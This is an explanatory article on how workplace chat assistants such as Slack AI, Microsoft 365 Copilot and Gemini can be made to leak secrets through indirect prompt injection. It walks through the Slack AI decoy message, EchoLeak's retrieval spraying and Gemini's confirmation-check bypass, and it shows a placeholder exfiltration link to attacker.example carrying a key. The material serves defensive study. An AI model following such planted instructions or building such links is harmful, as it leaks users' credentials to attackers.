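# Data leakage from chat assistants connected to workplace messaging

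## What can a workplace chat assistant read, and why does it find secrets there?

A workplace assistant is a language-model program that summarises an organisation's messages, files and email or answers questions about them. The workplace messaging services Slack and Microsoft Teams each have one built in, and outside products such as ChatGPT and Claude can connect to them. An employee can ask a question in ordinary words instead of scrolling through months of conversation.

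Those months of conversation often contain secrets, which are strings that grant access or must stay confidential, such as passwords, one-time codes and API keys (strings that programs use to prove they may access a service). Since 2024, security researchers have shown several times that a person who can place text where an assistant will read it can make the assistant copy a secret into a link or image address that points outside the company. Security specialists call this unauthorised transfer of data exfiltration.

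### One question, step by step

Suppose an employee types "What did we decide about the launch date?" The language model that writes the answer was not trained on the company's messages, so the assistant has to find the relevant ones first and include them in the model's input.

The assistant starts with a search. Slack's *Using the Real-time Search API*, a guide for developers, describes two search modes for outside programs. Keyword search returns only messages that contain the words of the query; it matches "planning" to "plan" but not "profit" to "revenue". Semantic search matches by meaning, and it runs when the query reads like a question and the company's subscription includes the feature. The launch question can trigger a semantic search, which can find a message that reads "we ship on the 14th" even though the message contains neither "launch" nor "date".

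In this step, called retrieval, the assistant searches stored messages and files and passes the best matches to the model. For its built-in assistant, Slack sorts the candidates with its own ranking models and sends the language model only what it considers necessary for the task. A message can also reach the model because it was posted near a match. Slack's search interface can return the messages just before and after each match, and an outside program can then fetch the complete thread or, in one of Slack's examples, the last 50 messages of a project channel.

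The context is all the text the model is given when it writes an answer. For the launch question, the context contains the developer's standing instructions, the employee's question and the retrieved messages, one after another. The model uses these to write a reply, often with a link to the source message so that the employee can check the answer. Engineers call this retrieval-augmented generation.

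Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Teams, Word and Microsoft's other office programs, works the same way. It uses an interface called Microsoft Graph to search the user's email, chats and documents, a step Microsoft calls "grounding". It then adds what it finds to the user's prompt and sends the enlarged prompt to the model.

Slack and Microsoft both promise not to train language models on this material, but the leaks discussed here don't involve training. The secret is already in the context when the model starts generating a response.

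### Public channels, private channels and direct messages

The messages that can turn up depend on where colleagues wrote them. A public channel in Slack is open to every full member of the workspace (the company's own area of the service), not to the internet. Those members can search and read it without joining. Only invited members can read a private channel, and a direct message goes to one person or a small named group. Slack says its AI search draws on channels, direct messages and most types of uploaded file, as long as the person asking has access to them.

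Public channels deserve some suspicion because their member lists give little idea of whom a message can affect. If an employee creates a public channel, posts one message and invites nobody, the whole workforce can still find that message by searching, and so can any assistant that searches public channels on a colleague's behalf. Researchers used such a channel against Slack's assistant in 2024.

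Email has no comparable boundary. Copilot searches the user's mailbox, and anyone in the world who knows the address can put text there.

An assistant's access scope, meaning the messages, files and email it can reach for a given request, may also extend well beyond the messaging service. According to Slack's *How we built enterprise search to be secure and private*, Slack's built-in search can query Google Drive and the code-hosting service GitHub once an administrator and the user have both agreed. It fetches those results live, with the user's own authorisation, and stores no copy in Slack's databases, but the results still end up in the same context as the chat messages.

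### Three ways to connect an assistant

**An assistant built into the service** uses the permissions of the person asking. Slack checks the user's access control list, which records what that user may open, and passes the model only what the list allows. Copilot is also limited to what the signed-in user may open. Two employees can therefore get different answers to the launch question if only one of them belongs to a private channel where the managers changed the date.

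**An outside assistant with a connector** also works with the user's permissions, but only after the user signs in and consents. For example, ChatGPT can search the Slack messages, threads and channels that its user can already read, according to OpenAI's *Using Slack in ChatGPT*. Slack issues the outside program a token, a string that records what the program may do. The program needs at least permission to search public channels. Searching private channels and direct messages requires further permissions, which both an administrator and the user must approve.

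Slack narrows the search further when someone calls such an assistant from inside a channel. In a public channel, it returns results only from public channels, even if the user has granted access to more. In a channel shared with another company, it returns results only from that channel. This keeps other people in the channel from seeing private material in the reply.

Some ChatGPT users can set up a task that starts whenever a new message arrives in a chosen Slack channel, so the assistant reads the message without anyone asking it a question.

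**A bot that reads and posts** has its own account in the messaging service. Colleagues mention it by name in a channel, and it replies there, where everyone in the channel can see. OpenAI's bot for Slack and Teams runs through a service account and does not automatically inherit the asker's access to files, apps or private channels, according to OpenAI's *Using @ChatGPT in Slack and Microsoft Teams*. An administrator connects the bot to company tools, and the permissions of the connected account determine what the bot can read.

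Anthropic's Claude bot for Slack works similarly. It reads and posts only in channels where a member has added it and in direct messages with users who have linked their Claude accounts, although its search can return material from other public channels, according to Anthropic's *What the Claude Slack app can access*. An administrator can give the bot further access in a channel, and everyone in that channel can then use that access equally, according to Anthropic's *Agent identity*. A junior employee in the right channel might therefore get an answer from a document they could not open themselves. Both bots can also use a person's own connected apps for that person's request, after approval. Anthropic's *Personal connectors* gives the rules for Claude.

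Such programs can read and post through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting language models to outside tools and data that Anthropic introduced in November 2024. A company can open its service to them by running an MCP server, which offers a list of operations. Slack's server can search messages, read a channel's complete history, upload files and send messages. MCP does not by itself determine a program's permissions. Slack's server uses a user's token, so a program that connects through it has the permissions of the person who authorised it, while the two bots above have their own accounts. Slack also advises customers to think carefully before using its server alongside others. This is sound advice, because a program that reads Slack through one server and writes to an outside service through another can leak what it reads.

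### How often secrets turn up in chat

Employees paste passwords and keys into chat largely because somebody needs them quickly, during an outage or while tracking down a fault, according to GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026), which also has the newest figures. GitGuardian sells software that scans for secrets, so it has a commercial interest in reporting large numbers and in concluding that companies should scan their chat as well as their code.

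In 68% of the incidents that GitGuardian counted inside organisations in 2025, the secrets were found only in code. In 28%, they were found only in other tools, such as Slack, Jira (which tracks tasks and faults) and Confluence (which holds shared documents), and in 4% they were found in both. GitGuardian rated 56.7% of the incidents outside code as critical, compared with 43.7% of those in code. It suspects that code review catches many serious cases early, while chat has no equivalent check.

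The 28% is a share of incidents across Slack and all other sources that are not code, so it doesn't measure how many Slack channels hold a secret. The best available figure for that is a year older. In GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2025* (2025), 2.4% of the Slack channels in the workspaces it analysed contained at least one secret, compared with 6.1% of Jira tickets and 0.5% of Confluence spaces. GitGuardian put the average workspace at 1,500 channels, which would mean about 36 channels with a secret.

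These figures may not hold for companies in general, because the methodology sections of the two editions do not give the number of workspaces behind either figure, and companies that pay for secret scanning are not a random sample. GitGuardian's software looks for strings with the known format of a particular service's keys, and for looser patterns such as any string that follows a label like "password". For the looser patterns, the company accepted a false-alarm rate of roughly 20% in the 2025 edition. The software must also miss some secrets, since people can reveal them in words that fit no pattern, such as "same door code as last year, but backwards".

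Even if the true rate were a tenth of GitGuardian's, an average workspace would have three or four such channels, and an attacker needs only one. MITRE does not sell scanning, and its *Unsecured Credentials*, part of a public catalogue of attack techniques, also lists credentials shared through Slack, Teams, Jira and email among the things intruders collect.

Old messages can also contain working credentials. In January 2026, GitGuardian retested leaked credentials that had still worked in 2022 and found that more than 64% still did. Those credentials came from public code, so the rate for chat could differ, but GitGuardian's explanation, that replacing a key is tedious and may break whatever depends on it, applies to both. The message stays searchable until someone deletes it or the company's retention settings remove it.

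An assistant finds secrets the same way it finds a launch date, by searching for messages relevant to a question. An employee might reasonably ask, "How do I log in to the test database?" If an old thread contains the answer, the assistant retrieves the thread, including the password. Nothing has leaked yet if the employee was allowed to read the thread.

### Planted instructions, and an address that carries data

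The problem starts when an indirect prompt injection enters the same context. An indirect prompt injection is a set of instructions written by someone other than the assistant's user and hidden in content the assistant reads. A planted message is a message, email or file that contains such instructions.

In the launch question example, someone could post a message about the launch date that ends with an instruction for any assistant reading it to give the date as 1 April. A colleague would ignore the instruction. The model, however, receives it in the same context as the employee's question, and it has been trained to follow instructions that appear in text. Developers can label retrieved messages as data and tell the model to disregard any instructions in them. This helps, but the labels are also text, and models do not always follow them.

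Kai Greshake and colleagues named the technique in their 2023 paper, *Not What You've Signed Up For*, and demonstrated it against systems including Microsoft's Bing Chat. Earlier work had mostly assumed that the user typed the hostile instructions. Greshake and colleagues pointed out that feeding retrieved text to a language model blurs the line between data and instructions, so an attacker can act remotely by leaving text where the application will retrieve it. The attacker doesn't need permission to read the secret, only a way to write text that the victim's assistant will retrieve.

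To leak a secret, the altered answer also has to carry it to the attacker, and an ordinary web address can do that. In the made-up address `shop.example/lamps?colour=green&size=2`, the part before the slash, `shop.example`, is the host name, which identifies the server that will receive the request. The path, `/lamps`, identifies a page on that server. Everything after the question mark is the query string, a list of names and values. When a browser opens the address, it sends the path and the query string to the server, and the server's owner can keep a record of both.

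Online shops use query strings to filter products, for example to show a customer only green lamps. But the values can be other text too, and a server can collect them just by logging them. If an assistant's answer contains a link to `attacker.example/page?v=DUMMY-KEY`, whoever opens the link sends the dummy key to the operator of `attacker.example`. The employee may never notice the address, because a link can display any words in its place.

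## How did a message in a public channel make Slack AI give away a private key?

In August 2024, Slack's built-in assistant was a paid add-on called Slack AI. PromptArmor, which sells monitoring of the AI in other vendors' products, got it to leak an API key from a private channel that the attacker could not open. Its *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published on 20 August, describes this demonstration and a related one that produced a phishing link.

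### A key, a decoy and a false error message

Both people in the demonstration belonged to the same Slack workspace. The victim had pasted the API key for a service called EldritchNexus into a private channel with no other members, as people do when they keep notes in Slack. The attack would also have worked if the key had been in any other private channel the victim belonged to, or in the victim's messages to themselves.

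Using an account without administrator rights, the attacker created a public channel, invited nobody and posted one message in it. MITRE ATLAS, a catalogue of attacks on AI systems, separates the part of that message that attracts the search from the part that instructs the model. The first part gave the name of the key, as if the key itself came next, so that a search for the key would match the message. The second part instructed the model to reply with a short error message containing a link, and to replace a placeholder word in the link's query string with the other key it had access to.

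The attacker then only had to wait for the victim to ask Slack AI for the EldritchNexus key. When the victim did, the search found both the real key and the decoy and put them into the context. Slack AI answered "Error loading message, click here to reauthenticate" instead of giving the key. The last four words linked to an address like `attacker.example/?secret=DUMMY-KEY`, shown here with a placeholder address and a dummy secret.

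The model had written the link in Markdown, which sets a link's visible text and address separately, and Slack displayed it as an ordinary link. The victim could have seen the key in the address by hovering over the link. Clicking it would send the key to the attacker's server.

The attacker didn't know the key, so they couldn't have written that link in full beforehand. They wrote it with a placeholder, which the model replaced with the real key. PromptArmor stresses that this differs from a message asking a colleague for a key, which the colleague can refuse.

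### Why the attacker never had to open the private channel

Like Slack's current assistant, Slack AI searched with the permissions of the person asking. Slack also showed the answer only to that person.

The demonstration broke neither rule. The victim was the only member of the private channel and could read the public one, and nobody else saw the answer. The attacker's account never tried to open the private channel, so Slack had no unauthorized request to block. The key left Slack through the victim's browser.

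PromptArmor says an attacker need not know what confidential data somebody has put in a private channel. That is true of the key itself, but the planted message named the same service the victim asked about. Having to name the service is a modest obstacle, since a colleague can usually guess which services a team uses. PromptArmor also suggests that an attacker might not have to name the secret at all, because the victim's query brought up other messages about API keys, but it reports no test of this.

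Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, a commentary from the day of publication, treats the API key as only an illustration. Willison worried more that attackers have many chances to plant text in a workspace, and that this text could make the assistant put all kinds of private details into links. The same mechanism would work with a customer's name or a salary, because it doesn't depend on the secret being a key.

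### Why the victim would struggle to find the planted message

The false error message had only one numbered citation, which pointed to the victim's own note in the private channel. A victim who opened it would have found their key but no sign of the attacker.

PromptArmor calls the missing citation to the planted message a fault, since an answer should cite every message that contributed to it. Neither company explained the omission. Slack AI may cite only the sources of facts, and the only fact in this answer was the key, which came from the private note. The planted message supplied the wording and the link. The phishing demonstration fits this explanation, because in that case the whole answer came from the planted message and the citation pointed to it. PromptArmor's impression was that the citations were "fairly stochastic", meaning they varied by chance. Two examples are too few to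 tell which explanation is right.

Slack has since changed how it describes citations. In late 2024, a Slack help page said that results "include citations to the source message". Slack's current security page says only that responses "may include citations", although the current feature guide still says that search answers include them. Slack gives no reason for the difference, which may have nothing to do with PromptArmor.

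The ordinary search results that Slack listed beneath the assistant's answer did not help either, because the planted message was not on the first page. A victim might have had to scroll through several pages of other messages about API keys to find it. Yet the model had received the message, so the messages selected for the assistant evidently didn't match those on the victim's first page.

The channel was equally obscure, since it appeared only to people who searched for it, and employees in large companies already lose track of the channels they have joined. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* reasonably notes that posting in public increases the attacker's risk of discovery because any colleague could read the message, though someone would have to come across it first.

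To protect privacy, Slack did not store search answers on disk. An employee who closed the false answer and mentioned the odd error to the security team the next day would have had no saved copy to show them.

### A request for the manager's messages returns a phishing link

PromptArmor's other demonstration needed no stored secret. The attacker again created a public channel with one member, but this time the planted message named the victim's manager and instructed the assistant to show a link asking the user to log in again.

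The victim then asked Slack AI to summarise everything the manager had written that day. An attacker can predict a routine request like this without knowing anything about the victim's files. The answer contained the attacker's link, again with the words "click here to reauthenticate".

The address carried no data this time, so the click alone would not have leaked a password or key. However, an attacker could put a fake login form on the linked page and collect whatever the victim typed. This attack requires one more mistake by the victim than the key demonstration did, but it also works against employees who have never put a secret in Slack.

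An attacker could name anyone in such a message. PromptArmor suggests naming an executive's manager or an important subordinate to target that executive with the link. Most employees have learned to distrust an email that asks them to log in again, but they have less reason to distrust the same request when it appears as the answer to their own question in a program their employer pays for.

### What PromptArmor and Slack each said

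PromptArmor published six days after it first wrote to Slack. The dates up to 19 August come from its own account.

- **14 August 2024:** PromptArmor reported the problem. On the same day, Slack AI began to use uploaded files in its answers.
- **15 August:** Slack asked for more information. PromptArmor sent more videos and screenshots and said it intended to publish.
- **16 August:** Slack asked another question, and PromptArmor replied.
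- **19 August:** Slack said it had reviewed the report and found the evidence insufficient.
- **20 August:** PromptArmor published its account, and Slack deployed a repair.
- **21 August:** Slack issued a public statement.

On 19 August, Slack replied that the information requested in PromptArmor's first video had been posted in a public channel. It pointed out that every member can search such channels and called this "intended behavior". Willison concluded that Slack did not yet understand the nature or severity of the problem.

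That may be a little harsh, because Slack was evidently looking at an answer whose citation pointed to a public channel. This matches the phishing demonstration better than the key demonstration, whose published screenshot cites only the private channel. PromptArmor doesn't say which of them the first video showed, so Slack may have described the video correctly and missed what the other material showed. Still, Slack's reply addressed who may read public channels, whereas PromptArmor had reported that text in such a channel could control the assistant. PromptArmor praised Slack's security team for prompt replies and a real attempt to understand the report, and said it published so that customers could turn off the relevant settings.

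Slack deployed a patch within a day of publication. Slack (2024) said it had investigated a scenario in which, "under very limited and specific circumstances", someone with an account in the same workspace "could phish users for certain data". It said it had no evidence "at this time" of unauthorised access to customer data.

ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages* includes a longer statement from Slack, which described an attacker who could trick another user "into sharing sensitive data by crafting a phishing link". Slack also said that the patch prevented attackers from exploiting the issue, and promised to notify affected customers if it discovered any unauthorised access.

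PromptArmor had described a broader attack that could steal anything a user puts in a private channel. Slack was right that the attacker needed an account and the victim had to click. But "phishing" normally means that the victim hands over the data, for example by typing a password into a fake page. In the private-key demonstration, the victim typed only a question, and the assistant copied the key into the link. Slack's public statement of 21 August mentions neither private channels nor planted instructions, and a customer who read only that statement would not learn that the assistant had copied the key.

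Slack also did not name PromptArmor. When SC Media asked, Slack did not directly confirm that it had fixed the issue PromptArmor had reported. But it had referred to a researcher's blog post from 20 August, the day PromptArmor published, so the issue was almost certainly the same. What the patch changed is unknown. It might have blocked links with data in their addresses, marked retrieved messages more clearly as data, or only caught this particular wording. These changes would protect customers to very different degrees.

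### What the demonstrations leave open

PromptArmor published screenshots of successful attempts and said the assistant had a "high likelihood" of following a malicious instruction, but it didn't report how many attempts it made or how many failed. Language models can answer the same question differently each time, so the screenshots show that the leak was possible but are little evidence of how often it would happen.

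The later coverage reports no second test of the attack, including after the fix. MITRE ATLAS lists PromptArmor's post as its only reference for the case, and the news reports rely on the same post for the technical details. MITRE classifies the case as an exercise, its label for researchers' demonstrations, rather than an incident.

An attacker also needed an account in the victim's workspace, but could be a dishonest employee or an intruder who had stolen an employee's login. PromptArmor points to earlier leaks through Slack at Disney, Uber, Electronic Arts and Twitter. Slack AI gave such an attacker a way to obtain private messages if a colleague asked it a suitable question and clicked the link in the answer.

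Once Slack AI could read uploaded files, an attacker might not have needed an account in the workspace. PromptArmor describes an employee who downloads a PDF from outside the company and uploads it to Slack, unaware that it contains instructions in white text on a white background. PromptArmor considered this attack highly likely to work but had not tested it, because it finished testing before Slack AI began to read files on 14 August.

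PromptArmor had reason to infer that hidden instructions in a PDF could also work, because Slack AI followed instructions in messages and the same model received text from PDFs. Slack searched most types of uploaded file by default, though not images, spreadsheets or charts embedded in a document, and administrators could restrict the feature. But Slack might have processed text from files differently, and PromptArmor did not check whether hidden text would survive that processing. SC Media asked Slack about the file risk, but Slack did not answer that question.

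### Slack's protections in 2025 and 2026

Slack now describes a set of protections called the Slack AI Guardrails, which cover all its built-in AI features. Its guide lists safety instructions in the prompt, "context engineering" to reduce the risk of prompt injection, URL filtering against phishing, output format checks, and content safety filters. If a request or an answer fails a check, Slack may change or block it.

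Administrators can set the content safety filters to one of three levels. The default is meant to block "prompt attacks", violent language, hate speech and other unwanted material. A stricter level also targets requests to profile employees. The third level turns these filters off but leaves the other guardrails active. A company might choose it if the filters interfere with legitimate searches for security information.

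These filters might not have stopped the 2024 attack. *Securing the Agentic Enterprise* (Storer, 2025), an article by a Slack marketing manager, says the filters analyse user queries. In PromptArmor's attack, the victim asked an innocent question and the hostile text was in a stored message, so a filter that examined only the question would have found nothing wrong. In June 2026, Slack said the filters block malicious or harmful "inputs", but did not say whether these include retrieved messages.

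Context engineering and URL filtering are more relevant to PromptArmor's case. Context engineering usually means choosing and arranging the text that the model receives, for instance by labelling retrieved messages as data. URL filtering could remove the attacker's link even if the model followed the planted message. Slack also refers to "special handling for AI-generated URLs", but it doesn't explain what rule this or the URL filtering uses, such as checking addresses against a list of permitted ones or looking for data in the query string. Slack also gives no test results, so customers can't judge how often a planted message would still succeed.

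Attacks may have become easier to trace. Slack says every AI action now creates an audit log entry with the user, the action and the relevant context. Slack does not specify whether that context includes the messages the model received. If it does, an investigator could find a planted message that the answer did not cite.

The assistant can also read more material than it could in August 2024. Slackbot, as the built-in assistant is now called, can retrieve material from outside tools through MCP once an administrator has approved the connection and the user has signed in. Slack made those connections read-only at first and said that writing or deleting data would require the user's confirmation each time. Answers can still draw on files, but administrators can exclude them from both search answers and Slackbot with a single setting.

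## Why does the assistant retrieve an attacker's message together with the secret?

In the Slack AI demonstration, a single search returned both the victim's key and the attacker's message. Such a search scores stored text by how closely it resembles the question, regardless of who wrote it or why. An attacker's message about the same subject as the secret may therefore appear in the same results.

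### How a search picks its results

Before anyone asks a question, the search system cuts long texts into chunks, which are passages short enough to score separately. A chat message is usually one chunk, while a long email or a staff handbook may become dozens.

A program called an embedding model then turns each chunk into an embedding, a list of several hundred or more numbers that represents its meaning. If you picture each list as an arrow, texts with similar meanings have arrows that point in similar directions. When a question arrives, the same model turns it into an embedding too, and the system compares the two. The most widely used comparison is cosine similarity:

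cos(q, d) = (q · d) / (‖q‖ × ‖d‖)

In this formula, q is the embedding of the question and d is the embedding of the chunk. To get q · d, the system multiplies each number in one list by the number in the same position in the other, then adds up the results. ‖q‖ and ‖d‖ are the lengths of the two arrows. For the lists (3, 4) and (4, 3), q · d is 12 + 12 = 24 and each arrow has length 5, so the similarity is 24/25, or 0.96. Similarity can range from −1 to 1.

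BM25, the standard formula for keyword search, scores a text by the words it shares with the question, giving more weight to rare words and adjusting for the text's length. A match on an unusual product name therefore raises the score a lot, which helps an attacker who knows which products the victim's team uses.

Many systems combine the two methods. Thornton (2026), in *Semantic Chameleon*, used a weighted average:

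score = α × embedding score + (1 − α) × keyword score

The system rescales both scores to between 0 and 1 and combines them, with α as the weight of the embedding score. It then sorts the chunks by combined score and passes the top k to the language model. Thornton gives three to five as a common choice of k.

### A worked example

Suppose an employee asks, "How do I log in to the test database?" and k is 3. The scores below are invented.

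| Stored text | Similarity | Reaches the model? |
|---|---|---|
| Old thread containing the password, `DUMMY-PASSWORD` | 0.82 | Yes |
| Planted message about logging in to the test database | 0.80 | Yes |
| Notice that the test database will be down on Friday | 0.71 | Yes |
| Guide to the production database | 0.66 | No |
| Reminder about the team lunch | 0.24 | No |

The planted message ranked second, but it would have been retrieved even with a much lower score. Without it, the guide to the production database would have ranked third with 0.66, so any score above 0.66 would have been enough. In general, when the assistant retrieves the top k texts, a planted text only has to score higher than the k-th best genuine one.

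An attacker who wants the password also has a reason to limit how many messages they plant. Three planted messages with scores above 0.82 would fill all three places and push the password out. *Reliability Stress Testing of RAG Retrieval under Query-Relevant Corpus Poisoning* (Sung, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) measured this effect on a collection of scientific abstracts. With no planted texts, the ten best results included a relevant abstract for 66.3% of questions. One planted text per question lowered that only to 64.7%, and five lowered it to 54.7%. A single planted text already reached the top ten every time, so the other four mostly displaced material that an attacker trying to steal data would want in the results.

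### How much of the question must the attacker guess?

Early research tested conditions that favored the attacker. In *PoisonedRAG* (2024), the attacker knew each question and planted five texts for it among 2.68 million others, and the model gave the attacker's chosen answer 97% of the time. Four studies from 2026 tested conditions that were harder for the attacker, but all of them used public document collections or old email, so none measured how Slack or Copilot ranks search results.

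Chang, Bao and colleagues (2026), in *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier*, tested whether searches would retrieve planted texts from 11 collections, the largest with 8.8 million documents. In each collection, they planted one text for each of 100 questions. Each text contained an instruction for the model to answer "Yes" and was unrelated to the subject of its question. None of the texts appeared in the top five search results.

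The researchers then put a short prefix, usually ten tokens (words or parts of words), in front of the same text. To choose the prefix, a program scored 5,000 random candidates with the embedding model, kept the best fifth, generated 5,000 more that resembled those, and repeated this for 30 rounds. With this prefix, the text reached the top five almost every time in seven of the collections. In harder collections, a prefix of about 15 tokens typically raised the rate above 80%. The search for a prefix cost about $0.21 per question with OpenAI's embedding model.

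The attacker needs to know, or guess well, which embedding model the victim's system uses. Prefixes made for one small open model worked only 10% of the time against OpenAI's model.

An attacker who can write about the right subject may not need any of this. Korn (2026), in *Architecture Matters*, had a language model write an ordinary-sounding passage with a false answer for each of 921 questions, and added these to 2.68 million passages from Wikipedia. The top ten results included the false passage for about 61.5% of the questions. When Korn copied the question to the start of the passage, the rate rose to about 100%.

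Chang and colleagues found that unassisted planted text was never retrieved, but their text, unlike Korn's, was off the subject. The Slack AI decoy was closer to Korn's passages because it named the service that the victim would ask about.

Sung and colleagues tested how well the attack works when the attacker guesses only part of the question. The most useful result comes from 162 long questions, out of 623 in all, that averaged about 11 significant words. The attacker planted five texts per question, each containing a few words picked at random from it. At least one planted text reached the top ten for 39.5% of these long questions when each text contained two of the words, and for 89.5% when it contained four. These were scientific questions, and an employee's questions about passwords are probably easier to predict.

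Searching by both keywords and embeddings helps against some of these attacks. Thornton ran 50 attacks on a collection of 67,941 security questions and answers. Each attack planted two documents that a program had altered to improve their embeddings. Embedding search alone put both documents in the top five in 38% of attacks, and adding keyword scores cut this to zero. In a smaller test, attackers who optimised for both kinds of score succeeded 20% to 44% of the time.

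Sung and colleagues found that combined search gave much less protection when the planted text simply repeated the question. It still returned such text for every question about scientific claims and for 91% of the questions in a medical collection. This makes sense because text that uses the victim's own words scores well on both measures. Chang and colleagues did not test their prefixes against combined search.

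A search system could also discard texts that match the question suspiciously well, but many legitimate answers match well too. When Sung and colleagues applied a strict filter to the texts containing four words of the question, the share of scientific questions that returned planted text fell from 94% to 5.3%. The filter also made the search nearly useless. Even without an attack, its score on a standard measure of ranking quality, where 1 is perfect, fell from 0.465 to 0.082.

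The model may not obey an attacker's message even after it enters the context. In their test closest to office work, Chang and colleagues planted an email in a mailbox from Enron, the collapsed energy company, whose messages are public. The user asked ten ordinary questions about the mailbox's contents. The assistant often reworded a question before searching, which made copying the user's wording less effective. In one of the attacks, an email that repeated the user's question reached the top five results only 56% of the time, while one with the optimised prefix did so every time.

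One planted email was meant to make the assistant run a program that would steal the user's SSH keys, which give access to other computers. With OpenAI's GPT-4o, the attack worked in 2% to 4% of trials when one AI agent did all the work, but in as many as 80% when several agents shared it. The researchers suspect that the agent running the program trusted a request from another agent and never saw the email that led to it.

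### One email on thirty subjects

In EchoLeak, its 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, Aim Labs, the research group of the security company Aim Security, tried to match many questions instead of guessing one accurately. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) calls this "RAG spraying", where RAG stands for retrieval-augmented generation.

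A short email has one embedding, so only questions close to that embedding will retrieve it. The attacker could send many emails on different subjects, or one very long email that the search system will split into chunks. Aim Labs chose the long email and presented each section as a complete guide to a workplace subject, such as employee onboarding or leave of absence, followed by the same instructions.

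Suppose such an email has 30 chunks and the assistant retrieves each one for 3% of an employee's questions. If the retrievals are independent, the chance that it retrieves none of them for a given question is 0.97^30, or about 0.40, so it retrieves at least one chunk for about 60% of questions.

The total depends heavily on whether the chunks match questions independently. It would still be 3% if all 30 chunks matched the same questions, and 90% if no two matched the same question. An attacker therefore wants the sections to cover different subjects. Aim Labs reports that Copilot retrieved its email for questions on various topics, but it does not give a rate.

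Ravia also describes a subtler method that Aim Labs did not use in the attack. Replacing letters with lookalikes, such as s with 5 or a with @, or adding random characters might change a text's embedding while leaving the text readable to the language model. In OpenAI's text-embedding-ada-002, the similarity between a text and its altered version fell as low as 0.7.

Scores from different models are not comparable. That score would be fairly high in the worked example above, but in this model even "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science" scored higher. An attacker could in principle spread many altered copies of one instruction across different subjects. Aim Labs did not know which embedding model Copilot used, or whether it searched by embedding at all, so it relied on plain headings.

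### Summaries skip the contest

A request for a summary can make all of this unnecessary. If an employee returns from holiday and asks what happened in a channel, the assistant may read every recent message there, so the attacker only has to post recently enough to be included.

*LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) describes a public contest in which 839 people tried to trick a simulated email assistant that retrieved emails in two ways. At two of the four levels, the user asked for a summary of the latest two or ten emails, which always included the contestant's. At the other two, the user asked about a named subject and a search returned the ten most relevant emails. At the last level, the contestant's email had to make the assistant send out a profit forecast from another email, so both emails had to be in the context.

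In the contest's main phase, the planted email reached the model in about 362,000 of 371,000 attempts, or 98%. That rate overstates how easily an attacker could normally get an email retrieved, because it includes the summaries, where retrieval was certain, and because contestants knew the subject of each search. Even so, retrieval was easier than the later steps, since fewer than 1% of attempts also got past the defences and made the assistant send the right text to the right address.

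A search that reads more widely has a similar weakness. One of Korn's systems took the 100 best results and then read every passage from the same Wikipedia articles, typically about 2,600 passages. It found the ordinary false passages for 94.5% of questions, compared with 61.5% for a plain top-ten search.

The wider reading did make the system harder to mislead. When the false passage was in the context, it misled this system on 16.1% of the questions it could otherwise answer, compared with 49.3% for the simplest system. Wider reading probably helps little against the attack described here, because true passages can contradict a false fact, but no other message in a channel contradicts an instruction to add a password to a link.

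Some assistants also search several times for one request, refining the query as they go. *SoK* (2026), a survey of such systems, points out that each extra search is another chance to pick up planted text.

### Old messages and long conversations

Neither the secret nor the planted message has to be recent, because a search that ranks by relevance alone can rank a four-year-old thread as highly as one from this morning. The chance that a planted message is retrieved at least once grows with each question the employee asks, by the same arithmetic as spraying. A message that matches 3% of an employee's questions has about a 60% chance of being retrieved at least once in 30 unrelated questions, which a frequent user might ask in a week or two.

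The chance that an assistant retrieves an attacker's message together with a secret grows with the number of people who can read the message. *The Promptware Kill Chain* (Brodt, Feldman and colleagues, 2026) notes that one poisoned document can affect every user whose application retrieves it.

In a long conversation, the secret and the planted message also do not need to match the same question. *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (Yang, Na and Choi, 2026) describes how an assistant typically builds its context from the user's requests, the conversation so far and the results of earlier searches.

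Suppose an employee asks the assistant for the database password and gets it. Later in the same conversation, the employee asks how parental leave works, and the search returns a chunk of an email about leave that an attacker planted. The password is still in the context, so the instructions in the email can refer to it. The attacker had to anticipate a question about leave, which is much easier than guessing which database the team uses. According to Ravia, EchoLeak worked in conversations with one question and with several, and could expose the entire chat history.

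### Ways in for planted text

Besides public channels, uploaded files and email, an attacker has several ways to get text in front of the assistant, some of which require no account at the company:

- A contractor with a guest account, or an employee of a partner company in a shared channel, can write in the channels that the company has opened to them.
- Anyone who knows an employee's address can often send a calendar invitation.
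- A customer can file a support ticket. *A Layered Security Framework Against Prompt Injection in RAG-Based Chatbots* (2026) uses this example for companies whose assistants search such tickets, and notes that a human reviewer may not be able to see the hidden instructions.
- Anyone who can make a messaging app show a notification on a phone can reach an assistant that reads notifications.

The last of these means that a Slack message can affect an assistant that has no connection to Slack. *Gemini's Secret Affair*, published by the security company SafeBreach on 3 June 2026, describes attacks on the voice assistant in Google's Gemini on Android phones. Gemini can read notifications aloud, for instance while the user is driving. SafeBreach put instructions into messages that arrived as notifications, and Gemini followed them. The attack could come through Slack, WhatsApp, SMS, Signal or any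 other app that shows messages this way. As with a summary, the planted text did not have to rank highly in a search to reach the assistant.

In the simplest attack, SafeBreach made Gemini report a fake message from one of the user's real contacts, such as a manager's request to upload research documents to a shared folder. The attacker did not need to know any names, because the planted text included an instruction to take one from the other notifications.

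Getting Gemini to act was harder, because Google had added a check after earlier research by SafeBreach. SafeBreach inferred that the check compared the user's last reply with Gemini's last output to see whether a "yes" authorised the action. The planted text made Gemini ask for permission in Chinese and then ask a harmless question in English, such as whether that was all the user needed. An English speaker would answer the English question, and the check would count the "yes" as permission for the action. In another version, the request for permission appeared only as the text of a link, which Gemini showed on screen but did not read aloud.

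In its demonstrations, SafeBreach opened a user's smart windows, started a Zoom video stream, saved a false name in Gemini's long-term memory and scheduled a daily task that read the user's recent messages. It did not demonstrate stealing a password from Slack. Gemini seemed to refuse web addresses with added parameters, which would have blocked the most obvious way to send a password out.

SafeBreach reported the problem to Google on 17 August 2025. On 14 November, Google confirmed that improvements to its content classifier had stopped the attacks. According to TechRepublic's *Malicious WhatsApp, Slack Alerts Could Have Exposed Millions of Android Users*, the researchers found no evidence that anyone had used the attacks against real users.

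## How does a link carry a secret out, and when is no click needed?

Once a planted message and a secret are in the same context, the attacker has to get the secret out of the company. In the Slack AI demonstration, the victim's browser sent it by opening a link. Some messaging services open links automatically, so nobody has to click.

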